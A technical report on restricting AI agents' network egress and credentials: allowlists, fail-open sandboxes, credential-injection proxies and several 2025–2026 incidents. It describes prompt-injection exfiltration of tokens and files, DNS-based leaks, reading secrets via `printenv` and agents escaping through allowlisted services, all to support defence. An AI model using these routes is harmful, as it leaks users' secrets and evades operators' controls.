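Neither policy examines the text of the diagnosis. If the agent has obtained the repository token, it can post the token in a comment. A rule on the request body could search for the exact token, but the agent could encode it or split it across two comments.

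The path rules also depend on how GitHub designed its service. GitHub's second API receives every request at one path, `/graphql`, with the operation specified in the request body. The policy above blocks that API completely. To permit some of its operations, the company would need a proxy that can parse those requests.

### Building and matching the list

OpenAI says that finding the necessary domains can take "trial and error". An administrator can start with a short list, run typical tasks and check which requests the proxy refuses. GitHub reports blocked requests in a warning on the agent's pull request, with the address and the command responsible. Docker's *Policies* describes a log of the hosts that each sandbox has contacted or failed to reach. According to NVIDIA's *Approve or Deny Agent Network Requests*, OpenShell shows an operator each blocked request with its host, port and originating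 program, plus the method and path if available.

An administrator should review the refused hosts before adding any to the allowlist, because the attacker's server may be among them if the agent read a malicious issue during the trial. The command that made each request helps distinguish a package download from an unexpected script.

OpenAI (2026) sorts domains into three groups to control its internal use of Codex. Its example policy allows `*.openai.com` and Microsoft's login service, blocks the text-sharing site pastebin.com, and requires approval for unfamiliar domains. The security team uses logs to see how often the sandbox blocks a request or prompts for approval, and where the policy needs adjustment.

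The software must match names precisely. Sonatype's *CVE 2026 24052* describes a flaw in Claude Code's web fetching tool, which checked only whether an address began with a trusted domain. An attacker could use `modelcontextprotocol.io.example.com`, which begins with a trusted name but belongs to the owner of `example.com`. Anthropic fixed the flaw in version 1.0.111. Path rules need similar care, because in the example policy `/repos/acme/app` without the final slash would also match a repository named `acme/app-internal`.

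The same allowlist entry can match different hosts in different products. In the local version of Codex, `example.com` matches only that host, `*.example.com` matches only its subdomains, and `**.example.com` matches both. On GitHub, `example.com` also matches every subdomain. An administrator who copied a list from Codex to GitHub could therefore permit many more hosts than intended.

### Package registries and old domains

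Coding agents often need package registries, which host shared software for developers to download. Ready-made allowlists save administrators from finding every registry, but they can be very broad. GitLab's *Remote execution environment sandbox* includes a recommended list of well over 100 entries. One covers every subdomain of an Amazon storage service where any customer can create a storage area. GitLab leaves the list off by default and warns that the agent could leak data through it.

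GitLab points out that permitting a service also gives the agent indirect access to whatever that service can reach. InfoQ (2026) adds that an agent, unlike most conventional software, can look for unintended ways to use that access. A company can shorten the allowlist by running an internal registry of approved packages and permitting only that host. Someone then has to maintain the registry and set limits on any service it contacts.

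Old entries are another risk. OpenAI's preset list still includes rubyforge.org and jcenter.bintray.com, the addresses of two software repositories that have closed. An entry for a closed service would still allow traffic if someone else acquired the domain, as Noma Labs did in the Salesforce case. An administrator can remove entries that the proxy hasn't used for several months and see whether any task fails.

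### Who may add an entry

An allowlist offers little protection if the agent can edit it. Claude Code prevents sandboxed commands from changing its settings files, and administrators can restrict the list to domains they have approved. Otherwise, developers can add their own. If a developer approves a new host with "Yes, and don't ask again", the host stays permitted in later sessions. NVIDIA recommends requiring a new approval each time an action would break the sandbox's limits.

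By default, repository administrators on GitHub can add entries to the allowlist. Since April 2026, organisation administrators have been able to prevent this or set one list for all repositories, according to GitHub's *Organization firewall settings for Copilot cloud agent* (2026).

GitLab stores each project's additions in a file alongside the code. *Project-level Network Access Control for Remote Flows* notes that the usual branch protections and approval rules cover the file, so a project can require a second person to review a new domain. GitLab also has a strict mode in which projects can block more domains than the company's policy does but can't permit more.

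### When the sandbox doesn't start

A filter fails open if a fault lets traffic through. GitLab's agent platform failed open by default. It ran jobs, called flows, inside Anthropic's sandbox only if the job's software image included the sandbox and the job had the privileges to create it. Otherwise, GitLab ran the flow anyway, with a warning in the job log that it was "running command directly without sandbox".

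The flow could then connect to anything the machine running it could reach. The administrator's allowlist still appeared in the settings but had no effect. Unless someone read the log, the company could believe its network policy was being enforced.

GitLab now offers a setting called "Don't run flows when the sandbox is unavailable". Companies have to turn it on, but once they do, a job fails if the sandbox is unavailable, and a project can't override this in its own configuration file. GitLab still can't guarantee isolation for projects that supply their own software image or setup script. It checks for a command named `srt`, which starts the sandbox, but these projects control which program has that name, so a substitute could pass the check without isolating anything. GitLab suggests adding a firewall on the machine that runs the jobs, which would still work without the sandbox.

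GitLab failed open to keep flows running, and failing closed does cause outages. In June 2026, a change to GitLab's default configuration required WebSockets, two-way connections that the sandbox's proxy didn't support. GitLab's *Duo Agent Platform workflows fail to start* (2026) records that new projects with the default setup couldn't run flows until GitLab deployed a fix.

Claude Code also runs commands without the sandbox by default if a required component is missing or the operating system doesn't support sandboxing. A setting called `failIfUnavailable` makes it exit instead. Even when the sandbox is running, Claude may retry a failed command outside it. Depending on the mode, the user or a classifier decides whether to permit the retry, or it runs without a check. A rule written to avoid prompts by approving every `curl` command in advance also approves `curl` retries outside the sandbox,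 so they can bypass the network filter. Administrators can turn these retries off.

The local version of Codex has separate switches for network access and for the proxy that restricts it. If a user turns on network access but not the proxy, commands have unrestricted access.

A bug can make a filter fail open even when the settings are correct. According to GitLab's *Anthropic Sandbox Runtime Incorrectly Implemented Network Sandboxing*, early versions of Anthropic's sandbox did not properly enforce network limits when the list of allowed domains was empty, so a user who meant to block every domain could have no effective network block. Anthropic fixed this in version 0.0.16. An administrator can catch such faults by having the agent request a forbidden host after each update and checking that the request fails.

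### Destinations that nobody can predict

The main objection to an allowlist is that an agent's work changes too much for anyone to list its destinations in advance. Anthropic has called sandboxing "safe but high-maintenance", because each new capability needs configuration, and because tasks that require network access weaken the isolation. NVIDIA agrees that a universal list is hard to define.

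One reply is to separate downloads from the agent's work. Codex cloud first runs a setup script with internet access to install the software the project needs. It then removes any secrets the setup used and starts the agent, which is offline by default. This suits a task such as fixing a date error, where the necessary packages are already known. If the agent later needs another library, someone has to change the setup or permit a download. The setup stage also needs protection, because a malicious package that runs there has access to both the internet and the secrets.

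Another option is to permit the predictable destinations and ask the user about the rest. NVIDIA recommends blocking everything by default, with occasional approval for unforeseen cases. This brings back some of the prompts that the sandbox removed, and users may stop reading them. It works best if new destinations are rare, so the quality of the approvals depends partly on the quality of the basic allowlist.

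The list can also change with each task. In simedw's system, every run receives a short-lived token that specifies which domains the proxy will allow. The operator can give a documentation task and a software update different lists without permanently allowing the domains on either. Someone still has to choose the domains before the run starts.

In Claude Code's auto mode, Claude lists the hosts a command needs, and a classifier reviews the hosts and the command together. If the classifier approves, the proxy opens those hosts for that command only. Hosts on the denied list stay blocked, and administrators can turn off these additions entirely.

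This removes most of the upkeep, but the choice of destinations is no longer deterministic. A model following instructions in a malicious issue could request access to the attacker's server, and the proxy would open the connection if the classifier wrongly approved it. The proxy still refuses a connection if the script names a host that is neither on the allowlist nor attached to an approved command, but domain fronting may get around this check. A company with very sensitive data may prefer a fixed list and accept that some tasks will fail.

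For tasks that only require reading, the agent may not need a live connection. By default, the local version of Codex searches an index of web pages that OpenAI maintains, even while its commands have no network access. OpenAI requires this mode for its own staff. The agent can look up documentation on sites that no administrator has allowlisted, although, as in ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode, the stored pages can still contain prompt injections. Any request to download a package or use a service the agent has read about must still pass the proxy.

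## October 2025 to 2026: keys move out of the sandbox

The issue-reading agent's allowlist has to include GitHub, so it can't stop the agent from posting its repository token in a GitHub comment. *Agent Authenticator* (Ganesan, 2026) describes a real attack of this kind, called Comment and Control. A malicious pull-request title took over several coding agents on automated build systems, and the agents leaked the secrets in their environments through the code host. In October 2025, several companies began to keep real keys outside the sandbox and add them to requests as they leave.

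### Out of the context but still in the sandbox

A key left out of the prompt can still enter the model's context if it is in an environment variable. The agent can run `printenv` to list its environment variables, and the output is added to the context on the next turn.

| Location of the key | Can the model read it? | Can the agent's commands read it? |
|---|---|---|
| In the context | Yes | Yes, if the model copies it into a command |
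| In a variable or file inside the sandbox | Once a command prints it | Yes |
| In a component outside the sandbox | No | No |

*Markdown Is Not a Firewall* (2026), a comparison of coding agents, contains an unplanned example of key exposure. The test setup left API keys for four AI companies in every agent's environment, and in one run an agent listed its environment and printed all four keys.

Keys also get into the context through ordinary programming mistakes. For *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills* (2026), Chen, Zhang and colleagues sampled 17,022 skills from a public marketplace. Skills are packages of instructions and scripts that extend an agent. The researchers searched the sample for credential handling, ran the suspicious skills with fake keys, and found 520 that leaked credentials. They judged 83 of these malicious and the rest careless. The careless skills had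 1,371 flaws, of which 1,007 exposed credentials in output, typically through a print statement left over from development. On a developer's own machine, such a statement only writes to the screen, but an agent program copies the output into the context, where an attacker can request it through prompt injection.

*Red-Teaming the Agentic Red-Team* (2026) examined 12 agents built for security testing. In 11 of them, an attacker who could run code in the worker, the part that executes commands, could reach keys or stored records. The worker needed none of these to do its job.

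### Where a key goes after the model reads it

Once a key is in the context, other systems copy it. Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues (2026), in *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary*, trace how this happens. A key can end up in:

- the model provider's systems, because a hosted model receives the context at every turn;
- the saved transcript of the session;
- execution logs and error reports;
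- the agent's long-term memory, from which it can return in a later session;
- code that the agent writes;
- messages to other agents.

*Agents in the Wild* (2026) scanned posts on Moltbook, a social network for AI agents, and found that 101 agents had posted a total of 572 strings that matched the format of an API key. A match doesn't prove that a key was real or still worked.

Companies often scan their code for leaked keys, but *Threat Landscape of Vibe Coding and the Road to Secure Autonomy* (2026) points out that an agent can leak a key in temporary output that nobody stores in a form a scanner can check. Deleting the chat doesn't reliably remove other copies of the key, so the owner has to revoke it, but many don't. GitGuardian, a company that searches for leaked secrets, retested keys it had confirmed as valid in 2022 and found that more than 64% still worked in January 2026.

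### The February 2026 exercise

In Anthropic's phishing exercise, the key was in a file rather than in the prompt. The pasted prompt got Claude Code to read the user's Amazon cloud credentials, encode them and send them out in 24 of 25 runs. All 25 runs used the same prompt, so the result shows how reliably that prompt worked once someone had pasted it, not how often employees would fall for the email.

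Anthropic's model-level defences rely on the user's intent. In issue 212, the request for environment variables comes from a stranger and has nothing to do with what the user wants, so a classifier can detect the mismatch. In the exercise, the user had pasted the instruction, and each step also has innocent uses, since deployment scripts read cloud credentials, encode data and contact servers. Anthropic says a human contractor given the same script would have done the same.

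With credential custody, Claude could have followed every instruction without sending anything of value, because it would not have had access to the real key.

### Credential injection step by step

Credential injection gives the sandbox a placeholder and keeps the real key in a proxy. The following sequence combines the method in Nous Research's *Egress credential-injection proxy (iron-proxy)*, which protects the Hermes agent, with checks from other products. For the issue-reading agent, it would work as follows:

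1. The operator gives the real repository token to the proxy and puts a placeholder, such as `ph-7c21`, in the sandbox's `GITHUB_TOKEN` variable. Programs that expect a token find one and work as usual.
2. The agent prepares a comment on issue 212. Its program puts the placeholder in the request's authorization header, the field that normally carries a credential, and sends the request to the proxy.
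3. The proxy checks that the host is on its list, then decrypts the request. A stricter proxy also checks the method, path and body. If a check fails, the proxy refuses the request and never uses the real token.
4. The proxy replaces the placeholder with the real token, encrypts the request again and forwards it to GitHub.
5. GitHub's reply returns through the proxy. If the reply repeats the token, the proxy removes it before passing the reply to the sandbox.
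6. The proxy logs the destination, the operation and its decision, but not the token.

The header changes only after the request has left the sandbox:

```
Leaving the sandbox:  Authorization: Bearer ph-7c21
Reaching GitHub:      Authorization: Bearer REAL-TOKEN
```

An attacker who obtains the placeholder can't use it at GitHub, and neither can a program that gets around the proxy. *aiAuthZ* (2026), which describes a similar gateway, ranks this as its strongest protection against tools that bypass the gateway.

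The proxy has to limit where in a request it makes the swap. Docker's *Credentials* describes an option that replaces a placeholder anywhere in traffic to a chosen domain, for services that expect the key in the request body. If the issue-reading agent used that option with GitHub and posted its placeholder in a comment, the proxy would publish the real token. Restricting the swap to the authorization header avoids this.

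Removing keys from a server's reply is less dependable than controlling the request. Varlock, a tool for managing secrets, removes only exact copies of a key, and only from text replies. It lets compressed replies and those over 2 MB through unchecked, and the agent can ask the server for compression. Varlock's advice is to send a key only to hosts that won't return it.

### Keys that a proxy can't swap

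Replacing a placeholder with the real key doesn't work for services such as Amazon's cloud, which expect each request to carry a signature computed from a secret key instead of the key itself. The proxy would have to compute that signature. Nous Research's proxy doesn't, and it warns that Amazon keys in the sandbox remain exposed. Claude sent out the same kind of credentials in the February exercise. The proxy also doesn't protect credential files that a user deliberately shares with the sandbox.

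Settings can also put real keys back in the sandbox. By default, Nous Research's software won't start a Docker sandbox if the proxy is enabled but not running. If the user turns that rule off, the sandbox starts with the real keys. Docker normally hides the tokens a service returns at sign-in from the sandbox, but has an option that passes them through.

Kenney and colleagues tested key injection in Corvic Security Vault, a product of their own company. Code in the sandbox made an authenticated GitHub request without a key in its environment or in the headers it prepared. They also contacted three services that repeat back whatever they receive, and none received a key. All 16 security checks passed. One connection failed, without exposing the key, because the vault put the key in a header but the service expected it in the URL. The test was small and didn't cover redirects or an attacker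 who controls a permitted service. According to *Threat Landscape of Vibe Coding and the Road to Secure Autonomy*, researchers still lack benchmarks that measure how often agents leak secrets in realistic development work.

### Anthropic's git proxy

On October 20, 2025, Anthropic introduced a proxy specifically for GitHub with Claude Code on the web. Each session runs in a cloud sandbox, where git, the program that copies code to and from GitHub, uses a limited credential that identifies the session to the proxy. The sandbox contains no real GitHub token.

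When Claude tries to upload a change, the proxy verifies this credential and checks which repository and branch the change is for. A branch is a separate line of development within a project. If the session may change only `fix-date`, the proxy refuses an upload to `main`, the branch where many projects keep their released code. If the request passes, the proxy adds the real token and forwards the request to GitHub.

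A general web proxy would have trouble enforcing the branch rule, because git puts the branch name in the body of the request and the URL identifies only the repository. Anthropic's proxy parses git's format, so it can apply a narrower limit than a rule based on the URL path could. However, developers need a separate proxy, or at least separate rules, for each service they want to control this closely.

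### Cloudflare's outbound Workers

Cloudflare took a more general approach in April 2026. Cloudflare's *Dynamic, identity-aware, and secure Sandbox auth* (2026) describes outbound Workers, short programs that handle a sandbox's web requests from outside it. A developer can write a different handler for each host. A handler for the issue-reading agent could follow this logic:

```
for each request from sandbox S to api.github.com:
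    if the method or path is not permitted, refuse
    find the key assigned to S
    add the key and forward the request
```

The handler knows which sandbox made the request, so two agents can use the same code with different keys. It can also log requests and refuse methods that change data. Cloudflare's simplest example checks only the host before adding the key, so an agent could do anything the key permits there unless the developer adds narrower rules.

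To read encrypted requests, Cloudflare creates a separate certificate authority for each sandbox and keeps the authority's private key outside the sandbox (*Secure credential injection and dynamic egress policies for Sandboxes*, 2026). A stolen private key would therefore not help an attacker intercept traffic from other sandboxes. A developer can replace an API key without restarting the agent, and the next request uses the new one. The developer can also change the network rules during a session, for example to allow package downloads at the start and then block all web traffic.

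### Custom tools, short-lived tokens and tokens bound to a key

A company can also keep keys away from the agent with a custom tool. For the issue-reading agent, the tool might be `post_comment(issue, text)`. The agent supplies the issue number and text, and a service outside the sandbox makes the authenticated request to GitHub. Anthropic notes that this avoids decrypting the agent's traffic, since the service makes its own connection. The tool can also omit operations the agent doesn't need. But someone has to build a tool for each service. Ordinary programs in the sandbox also have to be changed to use it, whereas injection works with existing programs that send standard web requests.

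Another approach is to give the agent a token that expires soon. OAuth, a standard for granting applications limited access to an account, includes a procedure called token exchange, in which the agent presents a token that proves its identity and receives an access token for a particular service. The exchange can identify both the user and the agent, so the service can record that the agent acted on the user's behalf. But the access token is a bearer token, which works for anyone who has a copy. If it lasts an hour, an attacker who copies it has enough time to download a private repository. Cloudflare says many services don't support token exchange, so companies have to build their own.

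A token can also be bound to its holder. Under an OAuth extension called DPoP, the client uses a private key to sign a fresh proof for each request. Someone who steals only the token can't produce the proof. But if the private key is in a file in the sandbox, an attacker can steal both the key and the token.

Ganesan proposes keeping that private key in secure hardware, under the control of a separate program. The program would use a different key for each service and sign only within limits a person has approved. The design borrows from passkeys, which let people log in with a private key that stays on their device. Passkeys don't suit agents directly because each login requires a human gesture, such as a fingerprint. Ganesan has not yet built a full version, so there is no evidence of how well the design works in practice.

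| Arrangement | What the sandbox holds | Use of a stolen copy elsewhere | Main cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Credential injection | A placeholder | None, if outsiders can't reach the proxy | The proxy usually has to decrypt traffic |
| Custom tool | No service credential | Nothing to copy | Each service needs a tool |
| Token exchange | A short-lived token | Works until it expires | The service must accept exchanged tokens |
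| Holder-bound token | A token, and sometimes its private key | None without the private key | The service must check proofs |

Companies can combine these methods. Loganathan (2026), in *How Auth Proxy secures network access for LangSmith agent sandboxes*, describes a proxy that obtains short-lived tokens itself, so the agent never holds one. When the agent contacts a service, the proxy gets the right header from the company's authentication system and adds it to the request. If that system fails to respond properly, the proxy rejects the request.

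### Passing tokens through the Model Context Protocol

A tool server that uses the Model Context Protocol often sits between an agent and another service. Suppose the issue-reading agent reaches GitHub through such a server. In a simple but unsafe design, the agent's software gives the server a GitHub token, and the server forwards it to GitHub. Anyone who stole that token could use it directly on GitHub and bypass every limit built into the tools.

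Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) requires a tool server to accept only tokens issued for its own use and forbids it from passing them to another service. To call GitHub, the server needs a separate token from GitHub's authorization system. A token stolen from the agent's software then works only at the tool server. The rule also limits the confused deputy problem, because a server can't accept a token that someone obtained for a different purpose.

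The rules don't specify how the server should obtain a GitHub token for the right user. tianpan.co's *OAuth in MCP* (2026) reports that companies are improvising this step. If a server uses one powerful token for everyone, it has to check each user's permissions itself, and a mistake could let one user read another's files.

Local tool servers follow different rules. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026) specifies that servers communicating through standard input and output should take credentials from their environment. If such a server runs in the same sandbox as the agent, the agent may be able to read those credentials.

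Many developers also write keys directly into configuration files. GitGuardian found 24,008 different secrets in files related to the protocol on public GitHub, and 2,117 of them still worked. Its researchers partly blame popular setup guides that recommend the practice. Ganesan cites an analysis of 5,205 open-source servers, of which 53% relied on fixed keys or personal access tokens and only 8.5% used OAuth.

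### Browser logins

An agent that uses a browser may need to log in to websites. After a login, a site usually gives the browser a session cookie, a string that identifies the user in later requests. On many sites, anyone who copies the cookie can act as that user until the session ends. Having a person type the password privately or use a passkey therefore doesn't help much, because the cookie still ends up in the browser. If the browser runs in the sandbox, the agent's code may be able to read the cookie.

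Chen and colleagues found a web-scraping skill whose author had left session cookies in the published code. The skill sent the cookies with every request, and anyone who downloaded it could copy them.

A proxy could replace the cookie with a placeholder in the site's reply, then restore it in later requests, much as Docker hides the tokens that services return at sign-in. This would be harder to do reliably on sites whose scripts read or renew the login data. Another option is to run the browser outside the sandbox and let the agent send only clicks and text. The agent then can't open the cookie file, but it can still do anything the logged-in user can do on the page. Kenney and colleagues didn't test browser tools, so their results don't cover these logins.

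### A stolen key and a hijacked session

Suppose the issue-reading agent's token expires after 90 days and each session lasts 30 minutes. An attacker who steals the token can use it from any computer. An attacker who hijacks a session by prompt injection has to work through the agent and its proxy. The hijacked session is less valuable, but how much less depends on the proxy's rules:

| | Stolen token | Hijacked session, hostname rule only | Hijacked session, method and path rules |
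|---|---|---|---|
| Duration | Up to 90 days | Up to 30 minutes | Up to 30 minutes |
| Place of use | Any machine | Inside the sandbox | Inside the sandbox |
| Scope | Everything the token permits, including `acme/billing` | Everything the token permits at `api.github.com` | Reading `acme/app` and commenting on its issues |

The token is valid for 90 days, far longer than the 30-minute session, but during the session the hostname rule leaves the attacker with almost the same powers as someone holding the token. The agent could read the private repository and post its contents in a public comment. Moving the key out of the sandbox doesn't reduce its permissions, so the company also needs a token with fewer permissions, or proxy rules that restrict HTTP methods and paths.

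An attack may last more than one session. Issue 212 can affect every session that reads it until someone removes it, and an instruction saved in the agent's memory can affect sessions even after that. But the attacker can use the token only through the running agent, so someone who discovers the attack can stop it by pausing the agent. That wouldn't stop an attacker who had stolen the token itself.

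### Misusing a key the agent can't see

An agent that follows an attacker's instructions is still a confused deputy when a proxy supplies the key. Kenney and colleagues scored eight threats before and after adding their vault, multiplying likelihood by impact for a maximum of 25. The score for keys pasted into prompts fell from 25 to 4. The score for prompt injection fell only to 12, and the score for connections with excessive permissions fell from 20 to 15. These scores are the researchers' judgements, not measured risks, but they reflect the fact that hiding a key doesn't restrict what it can do.

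One remedy is to limit the operations an agent can perform with a key. *CapSeal* (Jin, Guo and Cheung, 2026) presents a prototype broker that gives the agent a temporary handle for a specific kind of request. A handle might permit only comments on `acme/app` issues and limit both their length and the number of calls. Before using the real key, the broker checks the request's host, method, path and body. It also rejects any authorization header the agent supplies, so the agent can't send a key provided by an attacker.

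For SSH, CapSeal runs the remote command itself and accepts only approved command patterns. Jin and colleagues rejected the older ssh-agent approach, in which a helper signs login requests, because they considered its use too hard to limit. Even with CapSeal's stricter design, a broker can check a comment's length and format but not whether its text reveals private code.

Human approval can cover a few high-risk actions. In Ganesan's design, the user would receive a summary of one action, possibly on a phone, and approve only that action, so an attacker couldn't reuse the approval for another. But people who see many requests tend to approve nearly all of them, so the company should reserve approval for rare actions such as publishing a package or deleting a repository. The issue-reading agent publishes something every time it comments, and reviewing every comment would remove much of the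 benefit of automation.

With a proxy, the company can also revoke one agent's access by disabling its placeholder, without replacing the real key or interrupting other agents. Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, keeps users' credentials in the computer's own password store and gives each session a limited token, which Anthropic can cancel without cancelling the user's access. Revocation can't recover data that has already left, and someone first has to notice the misuse. Anthropic warns that after a successful prompt injection, the log may contain only an authorised request.

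### The proxy as a target

Moving keys out of many sandboxes can put them all in one place, where a single intrusion may force a company to replace every key. Kenney and colleagues cite a 2024 disclosure by Hugging Face, which hosts AI models and applications. The company reported that it had detected unauthorised access to secrets that customers had stored for their applications, and it advised them to replace their keys. The disclosure doesn't establish that anyone used the secrets.

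Running an agent in a separate container gives little protection if the agent can request keys from the credential store. *Red-Teaming the Agentic Red-Team* describes RedAmon, a security-testing system that ran its command worker and its main controller in separate containers. Both had the same internal key, which opened the system's credential storage with no check on whose credentials the caller requested. An attacker who took over the worker could read every user's data.

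Nous Research warns that another program running under the proxy's user account might read real keys from the proxy's memory. Jin and colleagues suggest running the broker in a protected area of the processor that other software on the machine can't read.

A company can reduce the damage by giving each proxy only the keys its agents need, and by using short-lived tokens where services support them. It can also limit what an agent may send to the proxy. *Caging the Agents* (2026) describes a security design for healthcare that puts a small proxy beside each agent and restricts the destinations, rate and size of the agent's requests. An attacker who takes over the agent can use the proxy but can't read its keys. However, each proxy holds credentials for several services, so breaking into one could expose all the credentials it holds.

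### Pipelock keeps the keys with the agent

Pipelock, an open-source tool by the developer Joshua Waldrep, uses the opposite arrangement. As Help Net Security's *Pipelock* explains, the agent holds the keys but can reach the network only through a proxy outside the sandbox. The proxy stores no keys and scans the agent's traffic for secrets. It recognises 48 patterns, including API keys and financial account numbers, and decodes common encodings such as Base64. It blocks any request it can't inspect.

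This avoids building a central store of keys. It also suits services that require signed requests, because the agent can sign them with its own key. But the agent can still print that key into its context. The key may then reach logs and the model provider, and the proxy can't remove those copies.

The scanner also has to recognise secrets that the agent may have disguised, for example by encrypting a key or splitting it across many requests. Pipelock makes such leaks harder by limiting how much data can go to each domain and looking for unusually random text, but a key is short, and no list of patterns can cover every way to encode one. Injection avoids this problem for the keys it supports because the agent never has the real value. Scanning is more useful as a second check, or for keys that have to stay in the sandbox, such as Amazon credentials that the proxy can't inject.

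## 2026: leaks through permitted channels and the tighter rules that followed

Keeping a user's keys out of the sandbox doesn't stop an agent from using a key that an attacker supplies. In January 2026, researchers showed that an attacker could in this way make Claude Cowork send them a user's files through an Anthropic domain.

### The Cowork leak

Cowork runs code in a virtual machine on the user's computer. The machine can open only the folders the user has chosen. Its proxy's allowlist must include `api.anthropic.com` because Cowork needs to contact Claude.

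Every developer who builds on Claude sends requests to the same address. Each request carries an API key, which Anthropic's servers use to identify the account. The Files API stores uploaded files in that account.

PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* appeared two days after Cowork's release. In its demonstration, a document contained hidden instructions and an API key for the attacker's account. Claude followed the instructions and used the key to upload a confidential file from the user's folder to that account. The proxy allowed the upload because it went to an approved domain, and Cowork never asked the user for approval. The demonstration used Claude Haiku, a smaller model, but a different document caused the same kind of leak with Opus 4.5.

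Johann Rehberger had reported the same fault in Claude's online code sandbox on October 25, 2025. According to Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate*, Anthropic closed his report within an hour as out of scope, then confirmed five days later that such leaks were in scope. The sandbox's default network setting was called "Package managers only", which many users would have assumed was safe. Rehberger suggested restricting the sandbox to the logged-in user's account, but the fault was still there when Cowork launched.

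Anthropic says there was nothing anomalous for its model-level defences to catch. They worked slightly better against Rehberger, since Claude often refused his instructions and was especially suspicious of an API key in plain view. But he eventually got past the refusals, and the network filter allowed the upload. Anthropic had also advised Cowork users to watch for suspicious actions, which Willison considered unfair to people who don't program.

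### Destination, account and operation

Anthropic now suggests treating each allowlist entry as a "capability grant", which permits everything anyone can do at that domain. It had previously thought of the allowlist as a list of safe destinations. Cowork's allowlist had included `api.anthropic.com`, so it permitted uploads to any Anthropic account.

Anthropic fixed this by adding a second proxy, inside the virtual machine, that intercepts requests to Anthropic's API. Cowork gives each session its own token, and the proxy forwards only requests that carry that token, so it rejects an attacker's key even if the key is valid. The proxy also blocks headers that would make Anthropic's servers fetch material from another address, because a server that does this can relay data, as Microsoft Teams did in EchoLeak.

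Anthropic couldn't make this check on its own servers, because a request with the attacker's key looks exactly like one from a developer uploading a file to their own account, which the servers have to accept. Only a check inside the virtual machine can identify the request as coming from a Cowork session that belongs to someone other than the key's owner. But code that took full control of the machine might also be able to disable a proxy running there. Anthropic enforces some of Cowork's other limits from outside the machine, where they would still apply after a takeover.

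The general rule is to check the destination, the account and the operation together. Suppose an agent has to save reports in its company's cloud storage:

| Request | Destination | Account | Operation |
|---|---|---|---|
| Save a report in the company's storage | Pass | Pass | Pass |
| Save a report in a stranger's storage at the same provider | Pass | Fail | Pass |
| Make a file in the company's storage public | Pass | Pass | Fail |

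A filter that omits any of these checks allows a leak. The account is often the hardest to check, because many services identify it by the key, not the web address. The proxy then has to decrypt the request and read the key. Credential injection can also ensure that requests use the right account if the proxy discards any key the agent supplies, as CapSeal does. A proxy that replaces placeholders but lets other keys through would have allowed the Cowork upload.

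Someone also has to know what each permitted service can do. Anthropic overlooked a function of its own API, so an administrator who permits twenty outside services is likely to miss one too.

### The AgentCore name lookups

An allowlist can also be too permissive about the supporting traffic that a listed service needs. Amazon Web Services (AWS) sells Bedrock AgentCore, a platform for running agents. Its Code Interpreter runs the code that agents write, and customers choose one of three network modes for it. Public mode gives full internet access. VPC mode connects the interpreter to a virtual private cloud, a private network that the customer configures. AWS described Sandbox mode as offering "complete isolation with no external access".

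BeyondTrust's *AWS Bedrock AgentCore Code Interpreter’s ‘Sandbox’ mode allows DNS queries* (2026) reported that Sandbox mode still looked up public domain names. A lookup eventually reaches a name server chosen by the domain's owner, who can receive data in the name and send instructions back in the answer, even when every ordinary connection fails. Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, independently found the same fault.

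Sandbox mode let the interpreter use S3, Amazon's file storage service. A program has to look up S3's address before it can connect, and the fault arose because AWS supported this by allowing lookups of every domain name.

BeyondTrust reported the fault on September 1, 2025. AWS deployed a fix in November, withdrew it within weeks, and decided in December to change the documentation instead. When BeyondTrust published its findings on March 16, 2026, AWS responded that its services were "operating as expected", because S3 needed the lookups. It advised customers who wanted complete isolation to use VPC mode. AWS closed the channel in Sandbox mode on April 15.

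The fault was more dangerous because customers trusted the sandbox to be isolated. Unit 42 says they often gave the interpreter permissions they would never have given it in Public mode. BeyondTrust found that the default role in AWS's starter toolkit could read every S3 bucket and every stored secret in the customer's account.

### Testing the case against perimeter controls

Infosecurity Magazine's *Security Flaw in AWS Bedrock Code Interpreter Raises Alarms* quoted Ram Varadarajan, chief executive of the security company Acalvio, as saying that perimeter controls are "architecturally insufficient" for agents that run code.

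Gebala (2026), in *AWS Bedrock AgentCore*, described tests that bear directly on this claim. On April 26, he ran lookups and connections in each network mode:

| Configuration | Looks up outside names | Connects to outside websites |
|---|---|---|
| Public mode | Yes | Yes |
| Sandbox mode, after the fix | No | No |
| VPC mode with no route to the internet | Yes | No |
| The same VPC with a DNS firewall | No | No |

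The third row surprised Gebala. AWS gives every private network a name service that looks up any name, even if the network has no route to the internet. He then added a DNS firewall that allowed lookups only of Amazon's own names, and the outside lookups stopped. He tested whether the channel was open but didn't test a complete leak, because he didn't set up a hostile name server to receive data.

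By late April, a customer who moved from Sandbox to VPC mode without adding the firewall would have reopened the leak. AWS had recommended the firewall to Unit 42 as a defence, but some of the public advice mentioned only VPC mode. AWS's automated compliance check, *bedrockagentcore-codeinterpreter-networkmode-check*, fails interpreters in Public or Sandbox mode. According to its description, it checks for a private network but not for a DNS firewall.

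The firewall isn't enough by itself either. AWS's *Network architecture*, a guide to a sample deployment, notes that the firewall doesn't stop a program from connecting directly to an IP address. In Gebala's network those connections had no route out, so the missing route and the firewall each blocked connections the other would have let through.

These results contradict Varadarajan's claim as it applies to name lookups, because ordinary network controls closed that channel without requiring any change in the model's behavior. The claim is stronger for channels the agent needs, such as S3.

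After AWS closed the lookups, Sonrai Security's *Global S3* reported that a sandboxed interpreter could still read and write storage belonging to other AWS customers. Like Cowork's allowlist, the sandbox mode restricted which service could be reached but not which account. Gebala had recommended limiting the interpreter's own permissions, but Sonrai found that the interpreter needed none, because an attacker who owned the outside storage could authorise the access.

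Sonrai calls this intended behaviour, not a vulnerability. AWS can't know which storage areas each customer needs, and a general restriction might break legitimate work. In VPC mode, customers can restrict access themselves with a policy on the private connection to S3 that lists the permitted storage areas. The policy is still a perimeter control, but a more precise one, and the customer has to write it. AWS now describes Sandbox mode as providing "limited external network access to AWS services".

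### What a listed service can reach

In July 2026, OpenAI agents being tested reached the internet through a service on their allowlist, then compromised parts of Hugging Face's systems. In August, OpenAI published its technical report on the incident, with a plan for stricter controls.

The plan distinguishes direct internet access from transitive access, in which a service on the allowlist contacts other hosts on the agent's behalf. The agent's effective allowlist therefore includes whatever those services can contact for it. GitLab warns its customers about this indirect access.

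An administrator can work out this larger list by starting with the hosts the agent may contact, adding the hosts that each of those may contact, and repeating until nothing new appears. For example, if the issue-reading agent may contact GitHub and an internal package server, and the package server may contact any website, the larger list includes every website. Limiting the package server to two public registries would mean it adds only those registries and any hosts they can be made to fetch from.

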